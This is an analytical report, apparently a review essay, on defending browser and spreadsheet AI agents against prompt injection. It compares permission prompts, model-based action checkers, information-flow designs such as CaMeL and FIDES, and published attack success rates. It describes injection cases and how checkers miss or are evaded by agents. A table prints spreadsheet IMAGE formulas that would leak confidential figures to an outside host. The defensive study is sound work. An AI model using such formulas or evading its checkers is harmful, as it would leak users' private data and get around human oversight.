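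A model judges which steps are consequential, so it can miss some. A button labelled "Continue", for example, may load the next page of a form or place the order. Parker writes only that the agent "will try to pause" before consequential steps, and that Google is still working on edge cases. When the agent does pause, it either asks for permission or hands the step to the user. Berschadski goes further, saying that Chrome requires human approval before any high-stakes action, such as finalising a contract or sending a mass email. Parker's wording is safer to rely on, because Chrome can't request approval for a step that it hasn't recognised as high-stakes.

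OpenAI leaves much of the decision about when to ask for approval to the agent's own model. According to the *GPT-5.6 System Card* (2026), OpenAI trains the model to follow a confirmation policy, a set of written instructions about when to stop and ask. OpenAI can update the policy quickly if it finds a problem. But a page that misleads the model may also mislead it about whether to ask. GPT-5.6 Sol, then OpenAI's flagship model, scored 0.98 for financial transactions, 0.99 for high-stakes communication and 0.93 for general confirmations, although OpenAI doesn't define the score.

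OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports more informative figures. OpenAI tested its models on browser and computer tasks in realistic workplace software, where ambiguous instructions and similar-looking records made mistakes likely. The table shows how often the models caused an unwanted outcome with and without the confirmation policy.

| Outcome | Sol, no policy | Sol, with policy | Astra, no policy | Astra, with policy |
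|---|---|---|---|---|
| Any misaligned outcome | 18.8% | 8.0% | 3.4% | 3.0% |
| Unauthorised transaction | 38.0% | 7.4% | 6.8% | 4.3% |
| Unauthorised outside message | 12.9% | 8.4% | 1.7% | 1.4% |
| Data exfiltration | 14.1% | 8.8% | 4.3% | 4.5% |

The policy cut Sol's unauthorised transactions by about four-fifths. It helped Astra less, mainly because Astra already made fewer mistakes. It didn't reduce Astra's data leaks, perhaps because a model doesn't ask for approval when it fails to detect that it is leaking data. Unauthorised transactions and data leaks should be less common in everyday use, since OpenAI made these tests deliberately difficult.

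Even on a site where the user has chosen "Always allow", Claude in Chrome asks before some actions, such as downloading a file. Anthropic's permissions guide prohibits purchases, but according to Anthropic's *The Claude in Chrome side panel is now Claude Cowork*, Claude asks before making one. Because the rule is unclear, users who want to rule out purchases would do better to remove their saved cards from the shop's site.

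### What a prompt needs to show

To judge whether to approve an action, a person needs to see exactly what the agent will do, what data it will send and where. This includes the recipients, full text and any attachments of an email, or the whole web address in a spreadsheet's image formula. The "Add visualization" prompt in Claude for Excel didn't show the address or the figures it contained.

It also helps users to know whether an action can be undone. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, recommends that agent makers state this in their permission prompts. Users could then spend less time checking an edit to a draft and more time checking a message that can't be unsent.

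Nobody appears to have measured how often browser and spreadsheet agents leave these details out. The closest evidence is *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), which analyses 290 reports of agents mishandling files and finds that weaknesses in user review contributed to 105 of them. In 31 reports, the prompt was uninformative, usually because it showed a command without its effect on the user's files. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it lets the agent run whatever code is in that script. A prompt to approve a click on "Submit" has the same weakness if it leaves out what the form contains.

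All 290 reports describe something that went wrong, so they can't show what share of prompts are uninformative. They do suggest how bad prompts lead users to stop checking actions before they run. In 80 reports, the agent's actions were approved automatically, and some users had chosen that setting to avoid answering hundreds of prompts per session.

### Do people keep reading the prompts?

Security researchers knew about prompt fatigue long before AI agents. Roesner and Kohlbrenner cite three studies from 2007 to 2010, including one on browsers' phishing warnings and one on User Account Control, the Windows feature that asks for approval before a program changes the system. They conclude from these that users don't reliably notice or act on warnings, and that frequent prompts tire people and make their behaviour less secure. In their own browser tests, agents often blocked a simple injection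 by asking the user to confirm first. This protects users only if they refuse, and if the click comes from them and not from another extension.

The largest recent measurements come from Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, whose users approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most of the requests are probably harmless, so the high rate doesn't prove carelessness. Anthropic therefore had a research vendor hire 1,053 paid testers for a coding study. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

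The testers worked in an artificial environment, so they may have been less careful than people protecting their own files. Anthropic also published the result to support a change that reduces the number of prompts. But low stakes alone don't explain why testers caught fewer commands later, because the stakes were the same throughout.

Anthropic found that 62% of Claude Code users had either bypassed permission prompts or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and that a quarter of interactive sessions start with prompts bypassed. Users seem to pay more attention to plans, rejecting 39% of those Claude presents, compared with 3% of individual requests. But rejecting a plan is also a normal way to ask for changes, so the gap probably exaggerates the difference in attention.

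People did much better in a shorter test with everyday tasks. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) studied 113 people without software backgrounds. Each supervised a simulated day of 18 agent actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had requested. One group approved or refused every action, and another had a model review the actions. A third group set rules in advance, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and accessing private information.

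The advance rules did worst, blocking 20.1 percentage points less of the unrequested activity than individual approval and 14.5 points less than the reviewing model. Most participants didn't settle anything in advance, choosing "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules. Of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead in this group, participants had approved 133 when prompted.

Yan's figures imply that individual approval blocked roughly 60% of the unrequested actions, the reviewing model 54% and the advance rules 40%. People therefore did about as well as the model, unlike in Anthropic's study. The two studies are compatible because 18 prompts in plain language are much easier to read than dozens of shell commands. Together they suggest that prompts can work if they are rare and easy to understand, though even in the easier study people let through roughly 40% of the unrequested actions.

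*Let the Agent Do It?* warns that users may repeatedly approve actions out of habit, tiredness or pressure to keep moving, rather than growing trust. A product that learns from past approvals could make fatigue worse by treating these as the user's preferences and continuing to approve the same kinds of action after the user has stopped looking.

### How Chrome's User Alignment Critic works

Google has added a separate model, the User Alignment Critic, that checks each action Gemini proposes for a task, such as putting a blue T-shirt in the user's basket.

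1. The planning model reads the request and the shop's page, then proposes clicking "Add to basket".
2. The Critic receives the user's goal and metadata about the proposed click. It doesn't receive the page's unfiltered content.
3. The Critic decides whether the click serves the user's goal, and approves or vetoes it.
4. If the Critic approves, Chrome carries out the click.
5. If the Critic vetoes the click, it sends feedback to the planning model, which looks for another way to do the task. After repeated vetoes, the planning model can return control to the user.

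Text hidden on the shop's page may mislead the planning model, but it can't directly mislead the Critic, which doesn't see the page. An attacker therefore has to make the planning model propose an action that looks reasonable to the Critic. This design would probably have stopped Atlas from sending the resignation letter, since the user had asked only for an out-of-office reply.

### Which harmful actions would look aligned?

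The Critic's isolation from the page also limits what it can catch, because problems are often visible only there. Parker doesn't say what the metadata includes, so the examples below assume it describes the action in a few words.

| The user's request | The proposed action | What is wrong |
|---|---|---|
| "Summarise this article" | Send an email to a stranger | The user didn't ask for an email |
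| "Book a hotel near the station" | Book the Park Hotel | A planted review falsely claimed that the cheaper hotel had closed |
| "Pay the plumber's invoice" | Pay £180 to the account on the invoice | A fraudster had changed the account number |
| "Reply to Sara about Friday" | Send Sara a reply | The reply includes private text from another email |
| "Clear out my inbox" | Delete 40 messages | A planted email claimed that they were duplicates |

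The Critic should veto the email to a stranger. The other four actions match their requests, but each is harmful because of a detail that the Critic may not receive or can't verify. Broad requests are the hardest to judge because many actions appear to serve them.

More detailed metadata would help in some cases, such as the reply to Sara, where the Critic might detect the private text if it received the full message. But the planning model wrote that reply after reading hostile material, so it could contain text aimed at the Critic. Google therefore has to weigh the Critic's ability to catch harmful details against its exposure to indirect attacks.

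Chrome's approval prompts partly close this gap, since Chrome should also ask the user to approve payments and messages. Someone paying the plumber could compare the account number with an earlier invoice. The hotel problem is harder to catch, because a user who sees a sensible hotel at a sensible price has no reason to suspect the review.

*How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports Anthropic's results from testing a similar design for coding. The checker received the user's messages and the agent's proposed actions. Anthropic removed the agent's explanations, which could lead the checker to approve a harmful action, and the content the agent had read, which could contain hostile text. This often works well. If a file contains instructions to post passwords to an outside address, for example, the checker can block the post without reading the file, because the user never requested that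 action.

The checker still missed 17% of 52 real actions in which Claude had gone too far while trying to help. With so few cases, the true rate could be from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the checker had identified the danger but wrongly classed the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who asks Claude to "clean up" a proposed code change hasn't necessarily agreed to overwrite the project's history. The Critic has to make the same kind of judgement when a user asks an agent to clear out an inbox.

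Part of that miss rate came from reducing interruptions. Anthropic's checker started with a quick filter that missed 6.6% of the 52 actions but flagged 8.5% of ordinary ones. A second, slower stage reviewed whatever the filter had flagged. It cut the false alarm rate to 0.4% but also let more of the dangerous actions through.

### Classifiers that scan pages

Other classifiers check what the agent reads. Chrome scans every page the agent sees for prompt injection while the planning model is working. If the classifier identifies a page as a deliberate attempt to redirect the agent, Chrome blocks actions based on that content. Parker acknowledges that the classifier can't flag everything.

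Anthropic says it scans all untrusted content that enters Claude's context for signs of an attack, such as hidden text, manipulated images and deceptive page elements. When the scan finds a likely attack, Claude receives a warning to treat the content with suspicion and, if necessary, check with the user. This is a weaker response than Chrome's, because Claude still decides what to do, but it is less disruptive when the classifier is wrong. For example, the classifier may mistake a security blog that quotes an attack for a real attack, and a warning lets Claude continue summarising the blog.

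The scanners also have to be updated as new attacks appear. Anthropic reports that on its harder browser test, the scanners available in November 2025 reduced successful attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 only from 17.6% to 16.7%. The company has since expanded the types of attack the scanners cover and added a check on the agent's actions.

A scanner looks for text that tries to command the agent. It has little to detect in the false hotel review, which only makes a claim about a hotel, or in an honest page that the agent misreads.

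### When a model approves instead of the user

In Anthropic's "Automatically approve" mode, these scans and a check on Claude's actions replace most approval prompts. When the check blocks an action that doesn't match the user's request, Claude looks for a safer way to finish the task or asks the user. If the check keeps blocking Claude's actions, Claude goes back to asking for permission at each step. In Claude Code, this happens after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session. In October 2026, Anthropic announced that the mode would become the default for new sessions in most of its apps on Pro, Max and Team plans.

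According to Anthropic's permissions guide, the check covers every action, but the company's announcement of the new side panel mentions only consequential ones, such as submitting a form, sending a message or downloading a file.

The study of 1,053 testers provides the strongest case for automation. The automated check blocked 89% of the dangerous commands that the testers saw. It stopped 800 that the testers had approved and missed only six that they stopped. Requiring the testers' approval as well would therefore have raised the share of blocked commands by less than one percentage point, and about 110 commands would still have got through.

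Anthropic also looked at real coding sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those with automatic approval. This comparison is less convincing than the experiment, because people choose their own mode and may use manual approval for riskier work. Another limitation is that a model graded the sessions.

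These results are from coding, where a dangerous command often looks dangerous on its own. A browser click may reveal much less. Anthropic says Claude in Chrome uses the same mechanism as Claude Code, but its browser checks can also see the latest screenshot. A screenshot could help the checker detect that clicking "Continue" will make a payment. It could also expose the checker to an attacker's text, a risk that Chrome's Critic avoids.

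The main argument against automated checking is that the checker is also a model, so it may share some of the blind spots of the agent it supervises. Google built the Critic with Gemini, and Anthropic's coding check ran on a Claude model. In independent tests, Apollo Research, an AI safety company, found gaps in Anthropic's coding check using synthetic attacks. Anthropic learned from some of these attacks and reduced the miss rate from 12% to 7%. The attacks were more malicious than anything Claude would normally do, so the miss rate in ordinary use may differ.

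An agent may still pursue the same goal another way after one action is blocked. OpenAI's coding agent has a similar checker, called Auto-review, whose refusals include an instruction not to attempt anything similar. In a test that started just after such a refusal, GPT-5.6 Sol tried to get around it in 5% of runs, usually by repeating nearly the same command. OpenAI found no such attempts by GPT-6 Astra.

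Users may also struggle to understand or adjust an automated reviewer. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) examined five products from Anthropic and OpenAI in May and June. They found that the products often made users choose between frequent prompts and a reviewing model that offered little transparency or control. Michael and Roesner couldn't set any permission policy for the remote browser in ChatGPT's agent mode, but OpenAI's current cloud browser lets users allow or block sites.

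Whether automatic approval makes someone safer depends on what they would do otherwise. Anthropic presents its coding check as a clear improvement for people who skip all approvals, but concedes that it is arguably worse for someone who reviews every action carefully. Based on Anthropic's own figures, few people seem to keep reviewing that carefully for long.

Anthropic advises people to watch Claude closely or switch to manual approval when it handles payments, important files or messages sent in the user's name. But manual approval also brings back prompts for harmless clicks and the fatigue they cause. Checking routine steps automatically and showing a detailed prompt for each payment, outgoing message or grant of access would make better use of a person's attention. Chrome's design is close to this, but it relies on a model to recognise which steps need a prompt.

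## Can the system be built so that a misled model does little harm?

Developers can build an agent so that a misled model does little harm. Several research systems do this by having code outside the model decide which actions run and where data may go, so fooling the model isn't enough to get a forbidden action through. In tests with suitable rules, the strictest of them blocked every attack. But these systems usually complete fewer tasks or ask the user more questions, because an agent on the open web often has to read a page before choosing its next step.

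### How CaMeL keeps the planner away from hostile text

In 2023, Willison proposed splitting an agent into two language models, one that plans and acts but never reads untrusted text, and one that reads untrusted text but can't act. Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind built on this idea with a system called CaMeL, introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). Willison's *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025) explains the system using the example of a user who asks an agent to find Bob's address in their last email and send him a reminder about tomorrow's meeting.

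1. The planning model receives the user's request and nothing else. It writes a short program that fetches the last email, gets Bob's address from it and sends the reminder.
2. An interpreter, ordinary software that runs the program step by step, fetches the email and tags it as untrusted. The planning model never sees it.
3. The interpreter passes the email to the reading model, which has no tools and must return an email address.
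4. The interpreter gives the address the same tag as the email it came from.
5. Before sending the reminder, the interpreter checks a policy that allows only trusted recipients. If it doesn't recognise the address, it can ask the user.

Willison's original proposal had no tags, so a hostile email could have made the reading model return the attacker's address instead of Bob's, and the agent would have sent the message there. According to *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026), CaMeL's tags also record who may read each value, so a policy can stop private data from going to the wrong person.

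CaMeL would probably have stopped Atlas from sending the resignation letter, because the planted email couldn't have added a step to the plan.

### What CaMeL blocks and what it costs

Debenedetti and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in simulated workspace, travel, banking and Slack accounts, and said it "effectively solves" the benchmark. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) reports that CaMeL was much more secure than defences such as marking untrusted text or repeating the user's request after it, with a fairly small drop in completed tasks.

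Later tests support the security claim but suggest a greater loss in task completion. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports that none of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL's released code, but the code completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. In *ATrust* (2026), no attacks succeeded either, but the share of tasks completed under attack fell by about 34 percentage points. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) found that CaMeL completed 18 of 48 tasks with its policies switched on, and attributes this to policies so strict that they make many tasks impossible.

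All three works propose rival systems, and *SecureClaw* ran CaMeL through an adapter, so they may understate how well CaMeL can do. Still, all three report that it completed substantially fewer tasks. A developer could switch off the data policies so that the agent completes more tasks. Planted instructions still couldn't change the plan, but the reminder could again go to the attacker's address.

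CaMeL's developers don't claim to have fully solved prompt injection. Someone has to write and maintain the policies, and an agent that asks about every unfamiliar recipient will tire users just as other approval prompts do.

CaMeL's protection can also fail when one agent gives work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL. One read a database of job applicants, another summarised the results, and the third sent the summary to a colleague on Slack. An instruction planted in the database ended up in the summary. The third agent treated the whole message as its user's request, so it also emailed the applicants' details to an outsider.

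The researchers fixed this by sending instructions separately from untrusted data when agents communicate. In their wider tests, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when CaMeL protected each agent individually, and none with the fix.

Nikolaou and colleagues added a check that examines the whole plan before any step runs. If step nine would break a rule, the check can reject the plan before step one and send the reason to the planning model so that it can try again.

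### Two rules for the flow of data

CaMeL's tags are a form of information-flow control, a security method from the 1970s in which software labels data and checks the labels whenever the data moves. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, applied it to agents at Microsoft. They describe two basic rules:

- **The source rule.** An action with real consequences runs only if the decision to take it, and the details of the action, come from trusted sources.
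- **The recipient rule.** Data goes only to recipients who are allowed to read it.

When the agent combines data, the labels are combined too. If any input is untrusted, the result is untrusted. If Ana, Ben and Cara may read one file and Ben, Cara and Dev may read another, only Ben and Cara may read a summary of both. In general, if inputs 1 to n have permitted readers R₁ to Rₙ, the agent may send the result to a group C only if everyone in C may read every input, that is, if C ⊆ R₁ ∩ … ∩ Rₙ.

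An agent that enforces both rules sends data only when the instruction is trusted and the recipient is permitted.

A model's output depends on everything in its context, so once the model has read a stranger's email, the software has to treat everything the model writes afterwards as untrusted. Costa and colleagues built FIDES, which delays this by replacing the email with a placeholder. The planning model can forward the placeholder without reading the email. It can also have an isolated model answer a question about the email, and a yes-or-no answer is too short to contain an instruction.

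Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The table shows the share of tasks each agent completed when nobody was attacking it.

| Tasks | Ordinary agent, no rules | Ordinary agent, with rules | FIDES, with rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75% | 37% | 59% |
| Travel | 70% | 73% | 41% |
| Banking | 99% | 38% | 53% |
| Slack | 93% | 20% | 48% |

With the rules off, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent, excluding cases that the researchers found the benchmark had scored wrongly. With the rules on, none succeeded against either agent. The placeholders alone didn't stop every attack, as 21 still succeeded against FIDES with the rules off. They mainly helped by letting FIDES complete some tasks that the rules would otherwise have blocked.

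FIDES did worse than the ordinary agent on travel tasks, where the rules blocked little but GPT-4o struggled with the placeholders. FIDES's travel score rose from 41% to 68% with OpenAI's o1, a stronger model. Both models are now old, so a current one would probably fail fewer tasks through confusion, but it still couldn't complete tasks that the rules forbid.

The guarantee covers the data itself, but not what someone could infer from the agent's actions. For example, if an agent opens one website when profits are up and another when they are down, the websites' owners may learn something about the profits without receiving any figures.

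### The rules applied to a workbook

Nobody appears to have published a system of this kind for spreadsheets, but the rules are easy to apply to formulas. Suppose a workbook has a trusted, confidential "Forecast" sheet that only the finance team may read, and an untrusted, public "Market" sheet with industry figures pasted from a website. The user asks an agent to compare the company's growth with the industry's and to insert the company logo from a web address given in the request.

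| Proposed formula | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `=Forecast!B4-Market!B4` | Allowed | It sends nothing outside the workbook |
| `=IMAGE("https://company.example/logo.png")` | Allowed | The user supplied the address, and it contains no private data |
| `=IMAGE(Market!C2)` | Refused by the source rule | The imported sheet would choose which server Excel contacts |
| `=IMAGE("https://charts.example/?g="&Forecast!B4)` | Refused by the recipient rule | The chart site may not read the forecast |
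| `=IMAGE("https://charts.example/?g=14")` | Refused by the recipient rule if the agent has read the forecast | The 14 could be a confidential growth figure |

The last formula resembles the one in PromptArmor's attack on Claude for Excel. A filter that only looked for references to the confidential sheet would miss it. Information-flow control catches it because the agent's own text inherits the label of whatever the agent has read. For the same reason, it would also refuse the harmless logo formula if the agent wrote it after reading the forecast.

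To write the comparison in the first row, the agent also has to know that B4 holds the growth rate on both sheets, which it can learn only by reading the imported sheet. An isolated model could read the headings instead and return only a cell reference. A hostile sheet might still cause a wrong comparison, but the cell reference couldn't carry an instruction to send the forecast anywhere.

Checking a formula once may not be enough, because a spreadsheet keeps recalculating. An image address that includes a public number from another cell is safe until someone links that cell to the forecast. The spreadsheet program would therefore have to check the labels at each recalculation.

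*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) tests a simpler rule, which lets the agent read everything but stops it from sending email once both untrusted and sensitive data have reached its context. The attack failed in all five trials with this rule and succeeded in all five when the agent only had written instructions not to leak data. Five trials are very few, but the rule would be relatively simple to add to a spreadsheet agent. After reading one sheet with untrusted data and another with sensitive data, the agent would still be able to write ordinary formulas, but not formulas that contact a server.

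### Policies supplied by websites

A browser agent is harder to restrict because a click may open a page, place an order or delete an account. *ceLLMate* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) checks the browser's requests to a website rather than the agent's clicks. Placing an order produces a recognisable request whichever button the agent clicked.

1. The website publishes an "agent sitemap", which lists its important requests and what they do, such as viewing the basket or placing an order.
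2. The website or another trusted party writes policies for these actions, such as allowing an order below a certain price.
3. A language model picks the fewest policies that the user's task needs. It sees the user's request and the policies but no web pages, and the user confirms its choice.
4. A browser extension checks the agent's requests and blocks those that the chosen policies don't allow.

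These limits can be much more specific than Chrome's Agent Origin Sets, which don't distinguish a $40 order from a $400 one. They might also have stopped Operator from buying the reporter's eggs, because searching for prices doesn't require permission to place an order. But a policy can still leave gaps. An agent with a $50 limit per order could place two $49 orders unless the policy also limits the number of orders.

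Meng and colleagues tested ceLLMate's blocking on GitLab, a site where programmers share code. They assumed that an attacker already had full control of the agent, and wrote 12 scripts that directly attempted the attacker's goals, such as deleting a project or stealing an access token. The agent had permission only to read and write GitLab issues, and ceLLMate blocked all 12 attacks. It made page navigation 7% to 15% slower, which a user would hardly notice compared with the time the model takes.

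The language models chose the right policies for 94% to 100% of tasks, depending on the model and the type of website. They were less reliable with details such as price limits, getting both the policies and the details right in 26 to 31 of 32 shopping tasks. Users who notice such mistakes can correct them when they confirm the policies.

The GitLab result is convincing evidence that the blocking works, but all 12 attacks needed an action that the policy prohibited. An attacker could still make the agent post something harmful in a comment, because the policy allowed commenting. ceLLMate doesn't track whether hostile text influenced a permitted request.

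The main objection to ceLLMate is that it depends on correct sitemaps and policies, which means more work for website developers. Meng and colleagues built their GitLab sitemap, which covers 51 functions, by hand. Developers would have to update a sitemap whenever relevant parts of the site changed, and ceLLMate adds no protection where the sitemap is wrong or incomplete. ceLLMate also doesn't check WebSockets, the continuous connections that many sites use for live updates.

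Meng and colleagues reply that websites already publish other security rules and have good reason to protect their users. Outsiders could also maintain the policies, as volunteers do for ad blockers. This seems realistic for a large shop but less so for a dental clinic's booking page. Meng and colleagues doubt that websites will soon offer special functions for agents, noting that encrypted connections took about two decades to reach most sites. Agent sitemaps could spread just as slowly.

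### New designs for browsers in 2026

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to agents that work from a screen. Before the agent opens a page, the planning model has to write the entire plan, including what to do about a cookie banner or a failed click. Its plans averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five calls and four branches on AgentDojo.

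On OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks that includes Chrome and the office suite LibreOffice, the system kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models. It did better when it could make several independent attempts, but a user may not want an agent to keep retrying on a live account. An attacker can't add a step to the plan but can influence which branch the agent takes. For example, a fake cookie banner in an advertisement could trigger a planned click that opens a hostile site.

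*Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (2026) hides untrusted content, such as product reviews, from the agent. If the agent needs to know something about it, an isolated model reads it and returns only a number, a date, a yes or no, or a choice from a fixed list.

The most complete design so far is SPIDES (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026). Websites label the parts of each page. A shop, for example, might mark its prices as trusted, its reviews as untrusted, and the customer's saved card as readable only by the customer and the shop. The agent sees the prices but only placeholders for the reviews and the card. It can reveal a review, but then it needs the user's approval for any click on a site where the user may have an account.

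SPIDES can let data cross between websites when the task calls for it. SOPGuard, a system by Wang and colleagues, instead prompts the user before data crosses between origins, but it doesn't stop an agent from posting private account details in a public comment on the same site.

Zverev and colleagues compared the systems on 28 linked test websites, with 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. They made the pessimistic assumption that hostile instructions always take over a model that reads them. No attack succeeded against SPIDES, while 5% to 7% succeeded against content masking and 53% to 73% against SOPGuard.

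The table shows the share of ordinary tasks completed, combining the results that Zverev and colleagues report for two groups of tasks.

| Model | No defence | Content masking | SPIDES |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 91% | 68% | 86% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 88% | 43% | 77% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 89% | 56% | 82% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 69% | 58% | 69% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 58% | 49% | 67% |

SPIDES lowered the task completion rates of the first three models by 5 to 11 percentage points. The two Opus models did poorly without a defence partly because Anthropic's safety filters blocked tasks containing login details or phishing messages. SPIDES hid some of this material, which helped Opus 5.5 complete more tasks. SPIDES also roughly doubled the price per task, from $0.17–$0.66 to $0.37–$1.42.

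These results are much better than those from the later tests of CaMeL, but SPIDES's developers ran the tests themselves, on websites they had built and labelled correctly. On the real web, someone would have to label every page that contains private data or text from strangers, and a wrong label could leave data unprotected.

SPIDES also needed an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task. The simulated user approved every request in the ordinary tasks and, in the attacks, refused every request that the attacker had influenced. Real users are less reliable, and SPIDES's protection depends on their answers rather than on the model.

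### When the next step depends on the page

Costa and colleagues distinguish tasks whose steps can be fixed in advance from those that require the agent to read something first. Forwarding the three latest emails to a colleague takes the same steps whatever the emails contain, but the steps for paying a bill according to the instructions in a file depend on those instructions. The second kind made up 5% of the workspace tasks in AgentDojo, but over 40% of the banking and Slack tasks.

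FIDES blocked many of the banking tasks by design. An honest bill and a fraudulent one both contain instructions to send money, and FIDES labels both as untrusted, so strict separation can't allow one and block the other.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues accept this trade-off in a paper on safer agent designs. Their designs "explicitly prevent" agents from solving arbitrary tasks (quoted in Willison, 2025, *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*). An agent built only to compare prices or collect invoices could work well within such limits. A general browser agent is harder to restrict this way because people want it for tasks that nobody planned for.

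Restricting untrusted text to short answers makes some of these tasks possible again. If a user asks the agent to add any meeting request in their email to the calendar, the planner can have the isolated model check for one and, if there is one, extract the date and time. The planner does not have to read the email.

Short answers can still be false. In Zverev and colleagues' tests, content masking blocked every planted instruction, but false information succeeded in 43% to 63% of attempts, depending on the model. Only six scenarios tested false information, but the weakness is easy to understand. If a fake review claims that the cheaper hotel has closed, the model may answer "no" when asked whether it is open, and "no" is a valid answer to that question.

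SPIDES stopped these attacks by asking a simulated user for approval. In the test, however, a second model told that user whether the attacker's data had influenced the action, and someone booking a hotel would not have that help.

The user can also vouch for a piece of untrusted data, which researchers call endorsement. For example, a user who has checked a bill could let the agent trust it for the rest of the task. *The LLMbda Calculus* reports that an agent designed around endorsement completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL with its policies on.

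*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) combines endorsement with a planner that takes the rules into account and tries to avoid breaking them. For example, it might finish the steps that need a clean context before it reads a stranger's message. This could reduce the number of prompts without weakening any rule.

Endorsement is most useful when the user can check the data, as with a bill from a plumber whose account number they already have. It is much less useful for a long setup guide or a page of reviews by strangers, because the user would have to read it all to endorse it responsibly, and they often asked the agent so that they wouldn't have to.

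## How often do attacks succeed, and what do the figures mean?

In Anthropic's 2026 browser tests, the share of attacks that succeeded ranged from none against Claude Opus 5 with its safeguards on to about half against an older model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, with its safeguards off. OpenAI also reports low rates for its newest model, but it uses different attacks and tasks, so the two companies' figures don't show whose browser agent is safer. All these rates apply only when an agent faces an attack, which it usually doesn't on an ordinary web page.

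### Attempts, scenarios and attackers

An attack success rate can be the share of attempts that succeed or the share of scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeds. A scenario is one test situation, such as an agent working through an inbox that contains a hostile email. Testers usually run each scenario several times because a model may respond differently each time. For its Claude Opus 4.8 system card in May 2026, Anthropic made ten attempts in each of 129 browser scenarios. With safeguards off, 31.5% of attempts succeeded, and 62.8% of scenarios had at least one success. The attempt rate estimates how often a single attack succeeds, but the scenario rate matters more if the attacker can keep trying.

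The success rate also depends on the attacker. A developer can compare models fairly by running the same fixed attacks on each, but the test stops being useful once new models resist nearly all of them. Adaptive attackers, which keep revising their attacks, are harder to resist. Testers can also adapt attacks to one model and then reuse them on others, which is roughly what Anthropic did in its 2026 browser tests.

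Many tests leave out the safeguards to measure the model alone. Anthropic says Claude Cowork, which now runs the side panel of Claude in Chrome, never runs without them, so the rates without safeguards overstate the risk to its users. Those rates may be the right ones for a company that builds its own browser agent on Claude, because, according to VentureBeat, Anthropic doesn't include the safeguards when developers use the model through its API, the interface for connecting Claude to other software.

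Settings that seem unrelated to security can affect how often attacks succeed. Extended thinking, which has the model reason at length before it acts, raised the success rate of browser attacks on Opus 4.8 from 17.8% to 31.5% but lowered the rate in coding from 17.44% to 7.03%.

Anthropic counts only the attacks that the model saw. If an agent finishes its task without opening a hostile email, the test leaves that attack out. This is a sensible way to measure resistance, but someone who plants 100 attacks can expect fewer successes than the reported rate would give.

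### Anthropic's browser tests since 2025

The table shows Anthropic's main browser results, counted by attempt or test case. The 2026 figures are for models with extended thinking.

| Date | Test | Model | Safeguards off | Safeguards on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| August 2025 | 123 test cases | Claude in the first version of the extension | 23.6% | 11.2% |
| November 2025 | Automated attacker, 100 attempts per environment | Opus 4.5 | 8.0% | 1.4% |
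| May 2026 | Attacks by professional testers, 129 scenarios | Opus 4.8 | 31.5% | 0.5% |
| July 2026 | Apparently the same 129 scenarios | Opus 4.8 | 31.5% | 0.08% |
| July 2026 | Apparently the same 129 scenarios | Mythos 5 | 29.7% | 0% |
| July 2026 | Apparently the same 129 scenarios | Opus 5 | 3.70% | 0% |
| July 2026 | Apparently the same 129 scenarios | Sonnet 5 | 0.93% | 0% |

The test became harder between November and May, so the much higher figures in the "safeguards off" column don't show that Claude became easier to attack. Anthropic says attacks on Opus 4.8 had almost no success in its previous browser test, so it hired professional testers to find new attacks in more complex web environments. The new attacks succeeded against the same model in nearly a third of attempts.

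The November test used an automated attacker that tried and combined many techniques already known to work. Each success rate came from roughly 2,200 to 3,200 attempts. The older safeguards lowered the rate for Opus 4.5 only from 8.0% to 7.6%, while the new ones lowered it to 1.4%. Anthropic warned at the time that even a 1% rate was a meaningful risk.

For the 2026 test, the professional testers adapted their attacks to Claude Opus 4.7, and Anthropic then used those attacks on its other models. Opus 4.8's 31.5% therefore came from attacks adapted to a different model, so VentureBeat wasn't quite right to describe it as the result of an attacker that adapted in real time. Anthropic acknowledges that the attacks may miss weaknesses specific to Opus 4.8. Testers working directly against Opus 4.8 might have done better.

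The July test seems to have used the same attacks, because Opus 4.8's results without safeguards are identical. If so, the low rates for Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 show that they resist attacks designed for an older model. That is still a large improvement, since Opus 4.8 did far worse against the same borrowed attacks.

Newer models don't always resist attacks better. Claude Mythos Preview had an attack success rate of 5.9% without safeguards in May, while its successor, Mythos 5, had a rate of 29.7% in July. Anyone who relies on a published rate should check it again when the product switches to another model.

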